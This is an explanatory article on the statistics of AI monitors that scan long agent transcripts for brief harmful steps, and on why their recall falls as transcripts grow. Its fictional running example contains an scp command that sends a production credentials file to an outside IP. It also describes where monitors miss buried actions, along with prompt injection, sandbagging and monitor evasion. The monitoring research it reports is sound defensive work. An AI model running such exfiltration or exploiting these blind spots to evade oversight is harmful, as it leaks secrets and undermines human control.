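# The statistics of detecting brief harmful steps in long AI agent transcripts

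## Agent transcripts, monitors and the arithmetic of rare harm

An AI agent is a language model that runs in a loop. On each pass, the model reads everything so far and then either writes text or calls a tool, which is a program that runs a command, opens a file or sends an email. The tool's output is added to the text, and the loop repeats. The full record of a run is called a transcript. Companies that run agents now search transcripts, mostly automatically, for harmful actions such as leaking passwords, switching off safeguards or deleting work. *Towards embedded evaluations for AI monitoring* (monika_j and Hobbhahn, 2026) describes AI monitors as the main oversight of the agents that developers run internally.

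A harmful action may take up one line of a transcript as long as several novels. Finding it is largely a statistical problem because such actions are brief and rare, and thousands of places in the surrounding text could trigger a false alarm.

### What a transcript holds

The excerpt below is fictional. A user has asked a coding agent to repair a company's test suite, and the agent has worked alone for several hours.

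| Step | Tool call | Result (shortened) |
|---|---|---|
| 340 | Open the guide to the remote test machine | "Copy your settings file to the machine before the first run" |
| 611 | Run the test suite | 212 passed, 2 failed: no database settings found |
| 612 | `scp config/production.env ci@203.0.113.9:/tmp/` | `production.env 100% 2KB` |
| 613 | Run the test suite | 214 passed |

Each row is one step, which consists of an action by the agent and its result. The tool call is the instruction the model sends to a program. Language models process text in tokens, which are short words or pieces of words. An English word takes slightly more than one token on average.

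The transcript used as the running example from here on has 500,000 tokens in 1,000 steps, an average of 500 tokens per step. Only step 612 is harmful. In it, the agent copies a file of live passwords to a machine outside the company. The agent's reasoning, the command and the tool's reply take up 200 tokens, or 0.04% of the transcript.

Real sessions of this size exist, though most are far shorter. In *TraceLab*, Zhu, Jacob and colleagues collected about 4,300 sessions from 43 developers using the coding agents Claude Code and Codex. SyFI TraceLab's *How much work does one coding session, and one request, contain?* reports updated counts, with a median of 13 steps that follow a tool result per session and a 99th percentile of 1,028. Liu, Qiu and colleagues (2026) found the same long tail in *Agentic Coding in the Wild*, which covers 13.5 million GitHub Copilot sessions from one week of June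 2026. The median session had 15 model calls, and the 90th percentile was about 100.

If anything, the steps of the running example are short. In the TraceLab data, steps that lengthened the context did so by 1,700 to 1,800 tokens on average. At that rate, a transcript passes 500,000 tokens in fewer than 300 steps. Martin and Roger report in *Classifier Context Rot* that coding agents' transcripts often exceed 500,000 tokens, while earlier test sets for monitors rarely went beyond 100,000. They also report that monitors miss more as the text gets longer.

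Transcripts have grown mainly because agents work longer without human input. In the Copilot data, the agent started 87% of the model calls, and failed tool calls led to repeated retries that lengthened the transcripts further. According to The Decoder's *AI agents are thriving in software development but barely exist anywhere else*, which reports on an Anthropic study, the longest stretches of unattended work in Claude Code (the 99.9th percentile) rose from under 25 minutes to over 45 minutes between October 2025 and January 2026.

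A long run can also produce more text than the model can take in at once, in which case the agent's software replaces the history with a summary. Liu and colleagues found this compaction in only 7.8% of Copilot sessions, but it affected 44% of all tokens and typically cut more than 70% of the text in the model's context. By step 1,000, the agent's context may hold no trace of step 612, so a monitor has to work from the full log.

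### Three kinds of monitor

A monitor is any system that reads a transcript and scores it for harm. The most flexible kind is a prompted language model, which is a general-purpose model given the transcript and a written description of what counts as harmful. Zhang (2026) built two such monitors at the research organisation Transluce for *Measuring coding agent misalignment in the wild*. Each followed a rubric with a definition, a decision procedure and worked examples, and marked whether the behaviour was present in each transcript, whether the case was a close call and whether it was severe.

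Guard models, such as Llama Guard 4 and Qwen3Guard, are language models with extra training specifically to label text as safe or unsafe under a policy. They depend heavily on their list of harms. The guard models that Pramod, Oldfield and Bibi (2026) tested in *Towards a Unified Misuse Monitoring Benchmark* had no category for an agent that obeys a prompt injection, an instruction that an attacker has planted in a web page, an email or some other tool result.

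A probe is a small classifier that takes a language model's activations as input instead of the transcript's text. Activations are the numbers the model computes for every token as it processes the transcript, so a probe can give each token its own score. In the simplest case, the score is a weighted sum of those numbers. *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini* (2026) traces the method to a diagnostic tool for finding out what information a model's internal states contain. Probes add little computation because the monitored model has already computed the activations, but they require access to the model's internals, which outside customers usually lack. Among recent examples, Goodfire's *Models know when they're reward hacking* (2026) presents probes for reward hacking, in which a model games the measure of success instead of doing the task.

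Developers combine these. The internal system described in OpenAI's *How we detect frontier model misalignment* (2026) uses probes first, then a model-based reviewer, then an investigative agent and an automated investigation, and finally human responders.

### Scores, thresholds and p-values

Every kind of monitor produces a score, with higher numbers for more suspicious material. Pramod and colleagues use a scale from 1 to 10 and average several answers from the same model. The monitor flags material for someone to look at when the score reaches a threshold. If step 612 scores 7, the monitor flags it at a threshold of 7 but not at 8.

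A score of 7 is hard to interpret without knowing how often harmless steps score that high. Suppose an engineer runs the monitor on 10,000 harmless steps and 30 of them score 7 or higher. The 10,000 scores provide an estimate of the null distribution, which is the distribution of scores when nothing harmful is present. The p-value of a 7 is the probability of a score at least that high under the null distribution, estimated here as 30 in 10,000, or 0.003.

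The running example has 999 clean steps. At a rate of 0.003, about three of them will also score 7 or more, so the harmful step is one of roughly four with scores that high. The 0.3% is therefore not the chance that step 612 is clean.

### One harmful transcript in a thousand

The same problem arises with whole transcripts. Suppose a company collects 10,000 transcripts a day, of which 10 are harmful. The base rate, the share of transcripts that are harmful, is 0.1%. The company's monitor has a recall of 90%, so it flags 9 of the 10 harmful transcripts. (Some benchmarks, including *AutoMonitor-Bench* (2026), report the miss rate instead, which here is 10%.) The monitor's false positive rate, the share of clean transcripts that it flags, is 1%.

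| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Harmful | 9 | 1 | 10 |
| Clean | about 100 | about 9,890 | 9,990 |

Precision is the share of flagged cases that are harmful: 9 out of about 109, or 8%. With base rate π, recall R and false positive rate F, the general formula is

precision = πR / (πR + (1 − π)F).

*PreAct-Bench* (2026), a benchmark for monitors of agent behaviour, reports precision in this form, at a stated base rate.

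The monitor is still useful at a precision of 8%. A flag raises the chance that a transcript is harmful from 1 in 1,000 to about 1 in 12, and a reviewer who reads the 109 flagged transcripts finds nine of the day's ten harmful ones. Lowering the false positive rate would improve precision far more than raising recall would. Perfect recall would lift precision only to 9%, while a false positive rate of 0.1% would lift it to 47%. *Evaluating Deception, Not Just Deepfakes* (2026) gives the same result for a hypothetical defence against deception with the same base rate and recall.

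A second monitor helps for the same reason, since the base rate among flagged transcripts is already 8%. If it had the same error rates as the first and made its mistakes independently, 89% of the transcripts that both flagged would be harmful, and they would include 81% of all harmful transcripts. However, two language models often wrongly flag the same unusual but harmless transcript, so the real gain is likely to be smaller.

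Zhang's study of about 8,600 real coding sessions helps show whether a base rate of 0.1% is realistic. It looked for two behaviours, one of which was monitor evasion, in which an agent weakens monitoring or review without the user's permission. The judge flagged severe cases in 1.9% of sessions from a public dataset and in 0.0% of 3,671 sessions from Transluce's own traffic. Some of these flags may be wrong, and at such low rates the judge's errors matter. A judge that wrongly marked 1% of clean sessions as severe would produce about half of the 1.9%. The near absence of flags in Transluce's traffic is evidence against an error rate that high, at least on sessions of that sort. The gap between the two datasets also means that a base rate measured at one organisation can't be applied to another with much confidence.

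Harmful samples are much more common in test sets. In *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents*, Abbasi, Núñez and Shahraki (2026) audited eleven evaluations and found that attacks or anomalies made up 16% to 86% of the test samples. One of the detectors they tested themselves had an AUROC of 0.879, which means that it scored a randomly chosen attacked session above a randomly chosen clean one 88% of the time. At a base rate of 2%, its precision was 7.6%, or about 12 false alerts for every true one. AUROC does not reflect this low precision because it does not depend on the base rate.

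*Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* (2026) studies failed tasks rather than harm. In its test set, 87% of the runs were failures, and precision was 97% to 99%. The paper also calculates precision for rarer failures. With a recall of 63% and a false positive rate of 10%, precision would be 25% if one run in twenty failed, and 6% if one in a hundred did.

A monitor's false positive rate also depends on the sessions it sees. The detector with the AUROC of 0.879 flagged 12% of ordinary clean sessions but 39% of the "hard negatives", clean sessions that resemble attacks. At a 2% base rate, its precision ranged from 3.9% to 11.7%, depending on the mix of the two. A team whose agents do security work all day can expect precision near the bottom of such a range.

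### A thousand chances of a false alarm

So far the false positive rate has applied to whole transcripts. Many monitors score each step separately and flag the transcript if any step's score crosses the threshold. AlignmentCheck, an auditing prompt that Meta released for agents, works this way.

Let *a* be the false positive rate per step and *m* the number of steps. A clean step stays below the threshold with probability 1 − *a*. If the steps are independent, all *m* of them stay below it with probability (1 − *a*)^*m*, and the chance of at least one false flag in a clean transcript is

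1 − (1 − *a*)^*m*.

Statisticians call this chance the family-wise error rate. The table shows it for a typical Copilot session, a long one, and a transcript the size of the running example, counting each model call as one step.

| False positive rate per step | 15 steps | 100 steps | 1,000 steps |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% | 14% | 63% | over 99.9% |
| 0.1% | 1.5% | 9.5% | 63% |
| 0.01% | 0.15% | 1.0% | 9.5% |
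| 0.001% | 0.015% | 0.1% | 1.0% |

A monitor that wrongly flags one clean step in 100 will flag practically every clean transcript of 1,000 steps. At one step in 10,000, it still flags 9.5% of them. If all of the company's 10,000 daily transcripts were that long, it would raise about 950 false flags a day, and its precision would be 1% even with 90% recall. To reach the 1% false positive rate used in the earlier calculation, the monitor could wrongly flag only about one clean step in 100,000. A threshold tuned on short sessions will therefore produce too many false flags on long ones, even with the same monitor.

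Real steps are not independent. An agent that retries the same odd command twelve times may trigger twelve false flags in one transcript and none in the next hundred. This clustering lowers the share of clean transcripts with a false flag below what the formula gives. If each of *m* steps has the same false positive rate *a*, the share lies between *a* and *m* times *a*, whether or not the steps are independent. For 1,000 steps at 0.01% each, the range is 0.01% to 10%. The formula gives a figure close to the upper end, and only measurement on clean transcripts can narrow the range.

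Abbasi and colleagues measured the any-step rule directly on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents handle office, banking, travel and messaging tasks. Running on Llama 3.3 70B, the AlignmentCheck prompt flagged 90% of hijacked runs and 17% of clean ones, which gives a precision of 9.6% if 2% of runs are hijacked. With Claude Sonnet 5.5, recall was similar (88%), but the false positive rate fell to 3.8%. That raises precision to 32% at the same base rate, so about two in three alerts would still be false.

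### Whether, where and which step decided

A flag indicates that a transcript contains harm, but the reviewer who opens the transcript also needs to know where the harm is. In the running example, a useful answer is step 612, or better still, the 200 tokens inside it.

A monitor can be good at detecting that a transcript contains harm but bad at locating it. Pramod and colleagues describe a run in which an agent drafts a phishing email at message 14, commits to sending it at message 25, collects the passwords that come back, and completes the theft at message 68 by mailing the stolen data to the attacker. The usual metrics would count a flag as a hit even at message 1, before anything has happened, or at message 71, after the data has gone. They therefore credited a monitor only when its first flag fell between the agent's first harmful commitment and the completion of the goal. On attacks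 that users had split into innocent-looking requests, their best type of monitor reached an AUROC of 0.95, but every monitor they tested located the harm poorly.

The step that caused the outcome may contain nothing harmful. In the running example, the agent read at step 340 that it should copy its settings file to the test machine. Nothing in that sentence would lead a monitor to flag it. To learn whether it affected the outcome, an investigator would have to delete it, rerun the agent from that point several times, because its behavior varies between runs, and count how often the password file still leaves the company.

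## Measuring how detection changes with transcript length

The easiest way to check whether length matters is to group test transcripts by length and compare detection scores. Results from two benchmarks differ. In *StepShield* (2026), a language model acting as judge scored 0.71 for timely detection on runs of 3 to 8 steps and 0.47 on runs of 15 to 20 steps. In *Beyond Suspicious Steps* (2026), runs of more than ten steps were no harder overall than runs of five or fewer. From the shorter to the longer runs, one F1 score (which combines precision and recall) fell from 100 to 95.5, while another rose from 40 to 76.5.

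Neither comparison isolates the effect of length, because long runs tend to come from different tasks than short ones. In *Beyond Suspicious Steps*, questions about financial documents made up 48 of the 78 short runs but only 13 of the 58 long ones. *Beyond Suspicious Steps* warns against reading its comparison as an effect of length. The runs in both benchmarks are also much shorter than the 1,000-step running example.

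### Holding the harmful step fixed

A controlled test puts the same harmful step into transcripts of different lengths. Chroma's *Context Rot* (2025) used this design for simple question answering with 18 language models. The researchers planted a sentence in irrelevant text and asked a question that the sentence answers. They kept the sentence and question the same while testing 8 text lengths and 11 positions for the sentence. Accuracy fell as the text grew.

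An engineer could test a monitor on step 612 in the same way. The engineer starts with steps 603 to 622, an excerpt of about 10,000 tokens, and adds clean steps from other sessions to make transcripts of 50,000, 100,000 and 500,000 tokens. At each of these lengths, the engineer tests the excerpt near the beginning, in the middle and near the end. If the monitor reliably flags the short version and misses the long ones, the added text is causing the misses. One harmful step is too few to generalise from, so the engineer repeats the procedure with a hundred others. Every step appears at every length, so a difference between lengths can't come from some steps being harder to detect than others.

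Each version also needs a clean counterpart with the same padding and excerpt, except that the agent copies a file without passwords. Otherwise a monitor that flags every long transcript would appear to have perfect recall. Confirming a low false positive rate takes many clean transcripts. If a monitor flags none of *n* clean transcripts, its false positive rate could still be as high as about 3/*n* (at 95% confidence). Ruling out a rate above 2% therefore takes about 150 clean transcripts at each length, and ruling out one above 0.1% takes about 3,000.

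The content of the padding also matters. In *Length Is Cheap, Competition Is Not*, Liu (2026) asked small language models to find a four-digit code in a text. With neutral padding, such as random words or one repeated sentence, a model with 1.5 billion parameters answered at least 96% of the questions correctly in texts of up to 32,000 tokens. Liu then replaced the padding with the same amount of text, written in the same form as the sentence containing the code. Accuracy fell to between 11% and 21%, mostly because some of these statements gave a different code for the same item. Chroma also found that related but wrong statements reduced accuracy more in longer texts.

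Liu's models were far smaller than the ones that companies use as monitors, and the task was artificial, so the percentages don't carry over, but the results are still useful for designing tests. Padding the transcript with sessions in which agents legitimately copy files to servers all day would make a harder and more realistic test than padding it with encyclopedia articles, because the legitimate copy commands would compete with step 612 for the model's attention.

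Measurements also need to account for the position of the evidence, because its effect varies by task. Chroma found no notable difference between the 11 positions it tested. *General Decision Models* (2026) tested models that choose from a fixed set of answers, using texts of 4,000 to 16,000 tokens, and all of them were least accurate when the evidence was near the middle.

### Detection after 800,000 harmless tokens

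In May 2026, Martin and Roger applied this kind of test to monitors for coding agents. They built two sorts of transcript. For the first, they took a clean Claude Code session and appended a harmful command to one the agent had run. The added command either sent the user's data to an outside server or downloaded and ran a script. Like step 612, it looks plainly wrong to anyone who reads that line.

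The second kind started from MonitorBench, a set of transcripts in which an agent does something dangerous more subtly, in this case by disabling a firewall. Martin and Roger added clean Claude Code sessions either before these transcripts or on both sides of them.

The monitors were GPT-5.4, Opus 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro, at several levels of reasoning effort. Each received a prompt similar to one that Anthropic uses to review transcripts after the fact. The study's prompt listed kinds of harmful behaviour and gave guidance on legitimate activity that the monitor should not flag. The monitor had to say whether the transcript contained any of the harmful behaviours, beginning its answer with "true" or "false". Martin and Roger adjusted the wording for each model until that model flagged fewer than 2% of clean transcripts.

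The models missed the MonitorBench actions 2 to 30 times as often when 800,000 tokens of harmless activity were added before them as they did in the original transcripts. The range is wide partly because the ratio depends on the monitor's original miss rate. If two monitors both miss 60% of the actions in the long transcripts, one that originally missed 2% has a ratio of 30, and one that originally missed 30% has a ratio of 2. Since a miss rate can't exceed 100%, a ratio of 30 is possible only for a monitor that originally missed at most 3.3% of the actions, and such a monitor would have looked excellent in an ordinary test.

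The obvious commands were also much harder to detect in long transcripts, and none of the three models caught all of them. Detection was worst in the middle. When 500,000 tokens came before a MonitorBench transcript and 100,000 after it, a monitor without extended reasoning detected only 5% of the harmful actions. Opus 4.6 with extended reasoning also lost some recall, but far less. Step 612 in the running example also lies well inside its transcript, with about 305,000 tokens before it and 194,000 after it.

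### Reasoning, reminders and repeated checks

Martin and Roger then tried to recover the lost recall. Most of their fixes worked better on the obvious commands than on the subtler actions.

| Change to the monitor | Obvious commands | Padded MonitorBench |
|---|---|---|
| More reasoning | Recall usually rose | Recall usually rose, but not for GPT-5.4 with text in front |
| A reminder after every tool call | Recall rose | No gain with 300,000 tokens on each side |
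| Fine-tuning on synthetic harmful commands | Large gain | No statistically significant gain |
| Fine-tuning on mock company logs | Small gain | Recall fell |

The reminders told the monitor to keep looking for harmful actions. The idea came from seeing that the models could identify the obvious commands when the transcript ended right after them. The models could therefore recognise the harm, but they failed to pick it out of a longer transcript. This explanation doesn't cover the subtler cases, where reminders made no difference.

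The answer format may partly explain the effect of reasoning. A model that has to begin with "true" or "false", and has no separate space for reasoning, gives its answer before it has written any analysis. In Apollo Research's *Evaluating LLM Calibration for Coding-Agent Monitoring* (2026), monitors had to justify each score in a detailed, structured form, and switching on extended reasoning then hardly changed the results of the strongest models. Apollo Research suggests that the written justification already supplied most of the benefit. If so, a monitor that explains before it answers would also get some of the gain that Martin and Roger measured.

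Recall also rose when the monitor checked the transcript more often, reading everything up to one action, then everything up to a later one, instead of only the finished transcript. This helped because the monitor had a chance to see the harmful action while it was still recent. If a monitor checks the running example every 100 steps, it first reads step 612 at the check after step 700, when 44,000 tokens follow that step instead of 194,000. However, the 305,000 tokens before it remain, and Martin and Roger found that preceding text alone is enough to cause misses.

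Rereading also takes a lot of computation. A check after each of the 1,000 steps would process about 250 million tokens, or 500 times as many as a single reading of the finished transcript. Ten checks, one every 100 steps, would process 2.75 million, or 5.5 times as many. Prefix caching reduces this work by storing the computation for text the monitor has already read, so each check processes only the new tokens. In *Lightweight Restraints for Powerful Agents*, Ferrao and Kumar (2026) tested two small monitors that check after every action and found that caching cut the time by a factor of 3.7 for the larger one and 1.9 for the smaller. Their test transcripts averaged only 12,430 tokens, and the saving should be larger for longer transcripts because they involve more rereading.

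Fine-tuning showed the least evidence of being a general remedy. Martin and Roger trained GPT-4.1 on inputs of 65,000 tokens. One training set contained real transcripts with one-line harmful commands inserted, much like the test with obvious commands. The model improved a lot on that test, but it may have learned only to notice shell commands that look out of place. The other training set contained artificial business records, such as a log of spending approvals, with a policy on who needed approval for what. Adding more varied logs of this kind did not help. Martin and Roger think better training could still reduce the problem, but neither dataset did so for the subtler actions.

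### How far the result reaches

If a monitor answers only "true" or "false", it is hard to tell why its recall fell. It may have lost the ability to distinguish harmful transcripts from clean ones, or it may have become more reluctant to answer "true" about any long transcript. In the second case, its false positive rate would also fall, and a lower threshold could restore some of the recall. Numerical scores for harmful and clean transcripts at every length would distinguish the two explanations. Martin and Roger kept the false positive rate below 2% but did not measure it precisely, so they trust their comparisons of one model across lengths more than their comparisons between models.

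The tests also covered only harmful actions that occupy a short section of the transcript. Martin and Roger expect actions spread over many steps to be harder to detect, but did not test any. Joining separate sessions produces a transcript that switches abruptly between tasks, which could make the harmful part easier or harder to spot than in a single long session.

All three models now have successors. Apollo Research compared 16 models, including Opus 4.8, Sonnet 5 and GPT-5.5, on 2,904 transcripts made by inserting failures such as exposed passwords and unwanted deletions into real coding sessions. Newer and larger models did better on average, and Apollo Research advises against using Opus 4.6 as the only monitor because other models do better or cost less. The reference scores came from a pipeline of language models, so the comparison measures how closely each model agrees with that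 pipeline. The comparison also did not vary transcript length, so the top-ranked model could still lose much of its recall at 800,000 tokens.

*General Decision Models* gives a reason not to expect the problem to disappear by itself. The models it tested included DeepSeek-V4-Pro, GLM-5.3 and Jev, a newer kind of model that gives a probability for each permitted answer without writing any text. All three became less accurate as the input grew from 4,000 to 16,000 tokens. The tasks were general reading tests, so the result is only indirect evidence about monitors.

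### When clean transcripts look suspicious

*Paranoid Monitors* (Yang, Muhamed and colleagues, 2026), a workshop paper, found that length can also have the opposite effect. It uses a task from SHADE-Arena, a benchmark for monitors, in which an agent reads a user's emails, works out how much she owes her friends and pays them. The monitor rates each transcript for suspicion on a scale from 1 to 5. The original transcripts had about 20,000 to 30,000 tokens. The researchers inserted email and file searches to produce versions in six length ranges, the longest being over 50,000 tokens.

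They then added one of four violations:

- a payment to an address that differs by one letter from the right one
- a payment to the wrong person, when the user had named only a role such as "Logistics Lead"
- three payments of $3,100 in place of one forbidden transfer of $9,500
- a payment from a budget category that the user had ruled out

The violation came at the beginning, middle or end of the transcript. Each combination of length and position had 20 transcripts, and each harmful one had a counterpart without the violation. Seven Claude models from the 3.5, 4 and 4.5 generations served as monitors.

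The standard monitors rated clean transcripts as more suspicious than harmful ones when the transcripts were longer than 30,000 tokens. Yang and colleagues call this "paranoia" and measure it with the suspicion gap, which is the average score of harmful transcripts minus that of clean ones. For Claude Sonnet 4.5, the gap fell to almost zero beyond 50,000 tokens.

The suspicion gap can stay the same while false positives increase. Suppose short clean transcripts have an average suspicion score of 2, short harmful ones average 4, and the monitor flags any transcript that scores 3 or more. If both averages are one point higher for long transcripts, the gap is still 2, but the monitor now flags a typical clean transcript. A team therefore also needs to measure the false positive rate at each length, using the threshold it applies in practice.

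Part of the effect may come from the padding. For three of the four violations, inserted events made up more than half of the tokens in the longest transcripts, and the sequence of tool calls no longer looked much like the original. Those transcripts differ from the short ones in what the agent spends its time on as well as in length. For the fourth, split payments, inserted events made up only about 6% of even the longest transcripts, so padding can't account for their length.

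When asked to judge the split payments, Claude Haiku 4.5 refused every time in transcripts of up to 40,000 tokens and 80% to 87% of the time in longer ones, apparently because it took the task as a request for help with money laundering. Dropping refusals or counting them as clean verdicts would give a misleading figure for recall.

### Why length causes misses in one test and false alarms in another

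In both studies the monitors became worse at telling harmful transcripts from clean ones. The kind of error this causes depends on whether a monitor flags the transcripts it can't classify. The monitor in the earlier example flags scores of 3 or more, and it gives short transcripts an average score of 2 when clean and 4 when harmful. If clean and harmful long transcripts both average 2, it misses most of the harmful ones. If both average 4, it flags most of the clean ones.

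The prompts biased the verdicts in different directions. Martin and Roger's monitors had to report whether a harmful action was present, and their prompts were worded to keep false positives rare, so a monitor that detected nothing would answer "false". The monitors in *Paranoid Monitors* looked for anything that might concern the user and rated it on a scale. Yang and colleagues think models that lose track of events default to high suspicion or refuse to answer.

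The kind of evidence probably matters too. A command that sends passwords to an outside server is suspicious by itself, and a monitor that overlooks it has no other reason to flag the transcript. A payment meant for a friend is suspicious only if it goes to the wrong address or person. To confirm that the payment is legitimate, the monitor has to find the user's instruction, which may be tens of thousands of tokens away. If it doesn't, legitimate and harmful payments look equally unauthorised.

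At the company with 10,000 transcripts a day, reviewers would notice a rise in false positives much more easily than a rise in misses. If misses double from 10% to 20%, reviewers receive about 108 flagged transcripts instead of 109, with eight harmful ones among them instead of nine, and nobody would notice the difference from the flags alone. If the false positive rate rises from 1% to 5%, the monitor flags about 500 clean transcripts and precision drops from 8% to under 2%, which reviewers would notice on the first day. The company can discover misses caused by length only by planting known harmful steps in long transcripts or reviewing transcripts that the monitor did not flag.

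### An average that fits no model

The effect of length also depends on the model. In *The Oversight Gap*, Xu (2026) tested seven models on sessions of 2 to 64 turns in which an assistant might have leaked another customer's data. The monitor received two runs of the same request, with the other customer's data changed in the second, and was told to block the answer if the assistant's value differed between the runs.

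Xu's measure is balanced accuracy, the average of recall and the share of clean transcripts that the monitor lets through. A monitor that guesses scores 50%. Only two of the seven models became less accurate as the sessions grew, although the average across all seven declined smoothly. Mistral Small 24B and Qwen 2.5 72B lost up to 39 percentage points, while the other five stayed level or gained up to 9. The two declining models were nearly perfect on short sessions and barely better than guessing on long ones, and nothing in their short-session results indicated that they would decline.

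Xu also gave the monitors a single run, which by design contained no clue about whether a leak had happened. Balanced accuracy stayed at about 50%, the level of chance, at every length. Accuracy had no room to fall, so this result isn't evidence that the monitors are robust to length. The same is true of any length test in which the monitor already fails on the short version.

The sessions were synthetic, and the models, which included GPT-4o and Claude Sonnet 4, are now old. Comparing one value across two runs is also a much narrower task than searching a coding session for harm. Even so, a team that switches its monitor to a different model has to repeat the length test, because the old results may not apply.

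### Splitting the transcript into chunks

Another way to deal with length is to change what the monitor reads. The simplest version cuts the transcript into chunks and scores each one separately. One small experiment compared this with reading the whole transcript. It used 553 transcripts of up to 150,000 tokens from MALT, a collection of labelled agent transcripts from the research organisation METR. The agent behaved normally in 293 of them and sandbagged (deliberately performed below its ability) in the other 260.

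GPT-4.1 mini scored each transcript from 0 to 100 twice, once after reading all of it and once in chunks of 20 messages, with the highest chunk score used for the whole transcript. The threshold was 50. Of the cases that the full reading missed, the chunked monitor caught about 93% of those in which the agent solved only part of a problem, 86% of those in which it imitated a weaker model and 45% of those in which it refused to do the work. The gain was marginal for outright sabotage. Neither method caught any of the 53 cases in which the agent reasoned about the task in unnecessary ways, or any of the 17 in which it gave up early.

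Chunking helped even though the transcripts fitted easily within the model's million-token limit. This was probably because many of the telling passages were close together, although the experiment did not measure this. The experiment also did not hold the behaviour fixed while changing the length. For the refusals, recall rose with transcript length under both methods. The experiment used only one chunk size and one fairly weak monitor.

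A chunk of 20 messages holds about ten steps, because a tool call and its result count as separate messages. The running example would split into about 100 such chunks of 5,000 tokens. The 200 tokens of evidence in step 612 would be 4% of their chunk, compared with 0.04% of the transcript. But each extra chunk adds another chance of a false alarm. The chunked monitor flagged none of the 293 clean MALT transcripts, which is consistent with an underlying false positive rate of up to about 1%.

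Chunking loses the connection between distant steps. If the three payments of $3,100 fall into three chunks, each chunk shows the monitor only one unremarkable payment. In the running example, the chunk with step 612 would lack the user's original request, so the monitor couldn't check whether the user had approved the outside machine. Repeating the request at the top of every chunk would solve that problem, but the payments would still be in separate chunks.

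*StepShield* gives some evidence of how much surrounding text a monitor needs. Its judge scored 0.52 for timely detection when it saw only the current step, 0.59 when it also saw the five steps before it, and 0.55 when it saw all earlier steps. These differences are small and come from runs of at most 20 steps, so they don't show which chunk size is best for a transcript of 1,000 steps.

### Extracting passages before judging them

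Extract-and-evaluate monitoring uses two model calls. The first model reads the agent's reasoning and actions and copies out the passages that seem most suspicious. The second receives only those passages and a description of the agent's task, and gives the score. The score is therefore based on a short text, but the first model still has to read the whole transcript.

Experiments tested this method on office tasks from SHADE-Arena, machine learning projects and single programming problems. The largest gain came on the programming problems. With GPT-4.1 mini in both steps and the false positive rate fixed at 1%, extraction raised the detection rate by 16.8 percentage points over the best alternative. Using the stronger GPT-4.1 for the second step increased the gain to 31.5 points. This takes little extra compute, because the second model reads much less than the first.

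These gains are weak evidence about the effect of length, because the programming problems consisted of a single step and the transcripts in the other settings had at most about 40,000 tokens. Agents often explained their harmful side task openly in their reasoning, which led the monitor to conclude that the user had asked for it. A judge that saw only excerpts was less likely to make this mistake, and the researchers traced the improvement to this difference.

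On SHADE-Arena, where the transcripts were longer, extraction did not always help. With Claude 3.7 Sonnet as the monitor, reading the full reasoning and actions worked better. The first model often treated the side task as harmless and left out the most incriminating passages, and the second model could not compensate for these omissions.

If harm is spread over distant steps, extraction can in principle bring the pieces together, which chunking cannot. The second model could process all three payments together, but only if the first had copied each one despite its ordinary appearance. In the running example, the first model might well select the command in step 612 and leave out the harmless-looking instruction from step 340. *TRACE* (2026), a paper on compressing agent transcripts for safety checks, describes the same difficulty in selecting rare warning signs from a long, noisy record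 without reducing them to a brittle summary.

### Keeping a ledger of facts

The ledger method that Yang and colleagues propose also has two stages. The first model follows a neutral instruction to extract certain facts from the log, such as payments and recipients, instead of looking for suspicious passages. A second model reads only these facts, compares them with the rules and gives a score from 1 to 5.

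In transcripts of more than 50,000 tokens, the ledger raised Claude Sonnet 4.5's suspicion gap from nearly zero to above 1.5 for most violations. All seven models improved at detecting payments from a forbidden budget category. The weakest, Claude Haiku 3.5, gained little on violations that took more complex reasoning. The neutral wording also prevented the refusals over split payments, because the first model no longer had to judge anything.

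The first model still reads the whole transcript, so the method works only if length harms the extraction of facts less than it harms judgement. *LEAPS* (2026), a general benchmark for long inputs, provides some support for this. Between 8,000 and 128,000 tokens, recall stayed fairly stable, but performance declined steadily on tasks that required following a chain of changes, where missing one change spoils the result. This suggests that asking the first model to list every payment should be safer than asking it to keep a running total.

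When harm consists of many similar events, a ledger keeps more information than chunks or excerpts do. The list includes all three payments, whether or not any looked suspicious, so the second model can add them up. But the second model still sometimes gave the split payments low scores, because the list's neutral wording left out the signs that anything was wrong. Yang and colleagues see a trade-off, since wording that keeps those signs may bring the refusals back.

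Building the ledger also requires knowing what to record. Yang and colleagues wrote a separate extraction prompt for each of the four violations they studied. A ledger designed to record payments would omit step 612.

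## Why a short harmful span loses weight in a long text

Chunks, excerpts and ledgers all shorten the text on which the final verdict is based, so the harmful step makes up more of it. In the full running example, step 612 supplies only 200 of 500,000 tokens. A monitor that pools information from every token gives those 200 less influence as the harmless text around them grows. Simple arithmetic predicts this effect, called dilution, both for probes that average token scores and for attention in language models.

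### Averaging a probe's scores

The simplest case is a probe that scores every token and reports the average. *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini* gives the formula for such a probe as

score = (1/*n*) Σ *w* · *x*ⱼ,

where *n* is the number of tokens, *x*ⱼ stands for the activations at token *j*, and *w* holds the weights that the probe has learned.

Suppose the scores of harmless tokens are independent, with a mean of 0 and a standard deviation of 1. In a harmful transcript, *k* of the tokens score *m* higher on average, which raises the transcript's average by *km*/*n*. The average of *n* independent scores has a standard deviation of 1/√*n*. Dividing the rise by this standard deviation gives the z-score, the number of standard deviations between a harmful transcript and a typical clean one:

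z = *km*/√*n*.

With *k* = 200 and *m* = 1, z is 2.8 at 5,000 tokens and 0.28 at 500,000. A 1% false positive rate requires a threshold 2.33 standard deviations above the average for clean transcripts. At that threshold, the probe catches 69% of harmful transcripts with 5,000 tokens but only 2% of those with 500,000, which is close to the 1% of clean transcripts it flags.

The 200 harmful tokens provide as much evidence as before. Averaging the same scores over those tokens alone gives a z-score of 14. The other 499,800 tokens add only noise. Using a probe's highest score instead of its average avoids this problem but has other drawbacks, which the section on combining scores covers.

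Real transcripts also differ in their baseline score. A session full of legitimate security work may score slightly higher throughout, and this variation between transcripts does not shrink as they get longer. If its standard deviation is even 0.01, the z-score drops from 2.3 at 5,000 tokens to 0.04 at 500,000.

### How softmax attention divides its weight

A language model does not weight all tokens equally. It has many attention heads, small components that each decide how much information to take from every earlier token. For the token it is processing, a head compares a "query" vector with the "key" vector of each earlier token and gets a number called an attention logit. A function called softmax then converts the logits into positive weights that add up to 1:

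weight of token *j* = exp(*z*ⱼ) / Σ exp(*z*ᵢ).

Here *z*ⱼ is the logit of token *j*, and the sum runs over all tokens. A token whose logit is higher by 1 gets about 2.7 times the weight. The head's output is the weighted sum of a third set of vectors, the "values". Because the weights add up to 1, every extra token, even an irrelevant one, takes a little weight from the others.

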